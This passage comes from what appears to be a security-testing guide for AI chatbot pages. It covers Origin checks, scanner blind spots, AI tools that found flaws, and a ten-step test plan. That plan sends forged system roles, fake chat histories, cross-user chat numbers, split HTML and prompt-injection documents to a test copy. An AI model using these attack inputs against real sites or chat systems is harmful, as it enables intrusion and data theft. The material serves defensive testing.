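TicketOracle tested server-side requests and left XSS for later work. The same reasoning applies to rendering flaws, since a cautious model may refuse to write hostile HTML but can't fix the flaw in the page. The choice of model makes no difference to a missing Origin check.

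### Scanners and AI testers

A web scanner can test the Origin check fairly easily by replaying the handshake with a foreign origin. The messages that follow are much harder to test. Each application defines its own, so the scanner needs recorded examples, a valid login and some way to recognise a harmful reply. A clean report may mean only that the scanner stopped after the handshake.

Developers can find out what their scanner covers by deliberately adding flaws to a test copy of the chatbot. They might turn off the Origin check, let one message type skip the ownership check, and see which of these flaws the scanner reports.

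AI tools found several of the 2026 flaws by reading code. Escape's agent downloaded the scripts of a chat page, found the part that rendered Markdown and searched it for the names of common sanitizers, but found none. It then found srcdoc by comparing the link filter's list of attributes with those a frame accepts. When rootxharsh and colleagues asked Claude Opus 4.8 to inspect the forum's image library, it discovered that the installed package lacked some security fixes. A researcher also used Claude to find the fake-cursor flaw in Open WebUI.

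These are real successes, but two of the three accounts come from companies that sell security testing, and they don't report how many flaws the tools missed or how many false alarms they raised. Anthropic's bounty rules require a working demonstration of every flaw and allow the company to close false or purely theoretical reports from scanners or AI. Developers who use such tools on their own code should also confirm each finding before changing anything.

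### A test procedure for chat.example

The testers need a copy of chat.example with the same settings as the live site, plus two ordinary accounts and an administrator account. They also need their own website on another domain that records every request it receives.

For most steps, testers should replace the model with a small stand-in program that returns whatever text they choose. Bullwinkel and colleagues advise developers to assume that a model given untrusted input can produce any output. The stand-in lets testers apply that assumption without having to get a model to write each test string. It also returns the same text every time, so a failed test is easy to repeat.

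The stand-in can also split a test string at every possible point:

```
for each test string:
    for each place where it can be cut in two:
        send the two parts as separate pieces
        wait until the page has drawn them
        fail if a script ran or a request left for an outside address
```

A string of 60 characters has 59 such places. If each takes half a second to test, 200 strings of this length take about 98 minutes, so the tests can run overnight.

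| Step | What to do | Safe result |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | List every host the page contacts and every place that displays an answer, including shared transcripts and the support console | The test covers all of them, with their owners' permission |
| 2 | Repeat the handshake with a foreign origin, "null" and a lookalike domain, then try from a page on the testers' website in several browsers | The server refuses each one but still accepts chat.example |
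| 3 | Log out, and separately demote the administrator, while a second tab stays connected | After the logout, the socket closes and the old login fails. After the demotion, administrator actions fail |
| 4 | As one user, put the other user's chat number in every type of message, including "stop" and "delete" | The server refuses, and its records show that nothing changed |
| 5 | Send an unknown message type, an extra field, a system role and a false chat history | The server discards them, and none reaches the model or the saved chat |
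| 6 | Send an oversized message, then start many long answers and disconnect | The server rejects the message and enforces the account's limit on answers |
| 7 | Use the stand-in to send HTML, links and images, whole and in pieces, then open the transcript as the other user and in the support console | No script runs, and no request leaves for an outside address at any moment |
| 8 | Run a preview that tries to open a window, contact the testers' website and send HTML to the main page | The browser blocks the first two, and the main page ignores the HTML |
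| 9 | Capture the packets of two answers with different word lengths | All messages have the same size and arrive at regular intervals |
| 10 | Restore the real model and run a prompt suite through the page, with some of the prompts hidden in documents | Even when the model obeys a hostile prompt, steps 4, 7 and 8 still give their safe results |

Developers can automate most of steps 2 to 8 and run them before every release. They should repeat step 1 by hand whenever another team adds a feature that displays answers, because an automated test checks only the places on its list. When the model changes, they need to repeat only step 10, unless the new model comes with new tools or message types.
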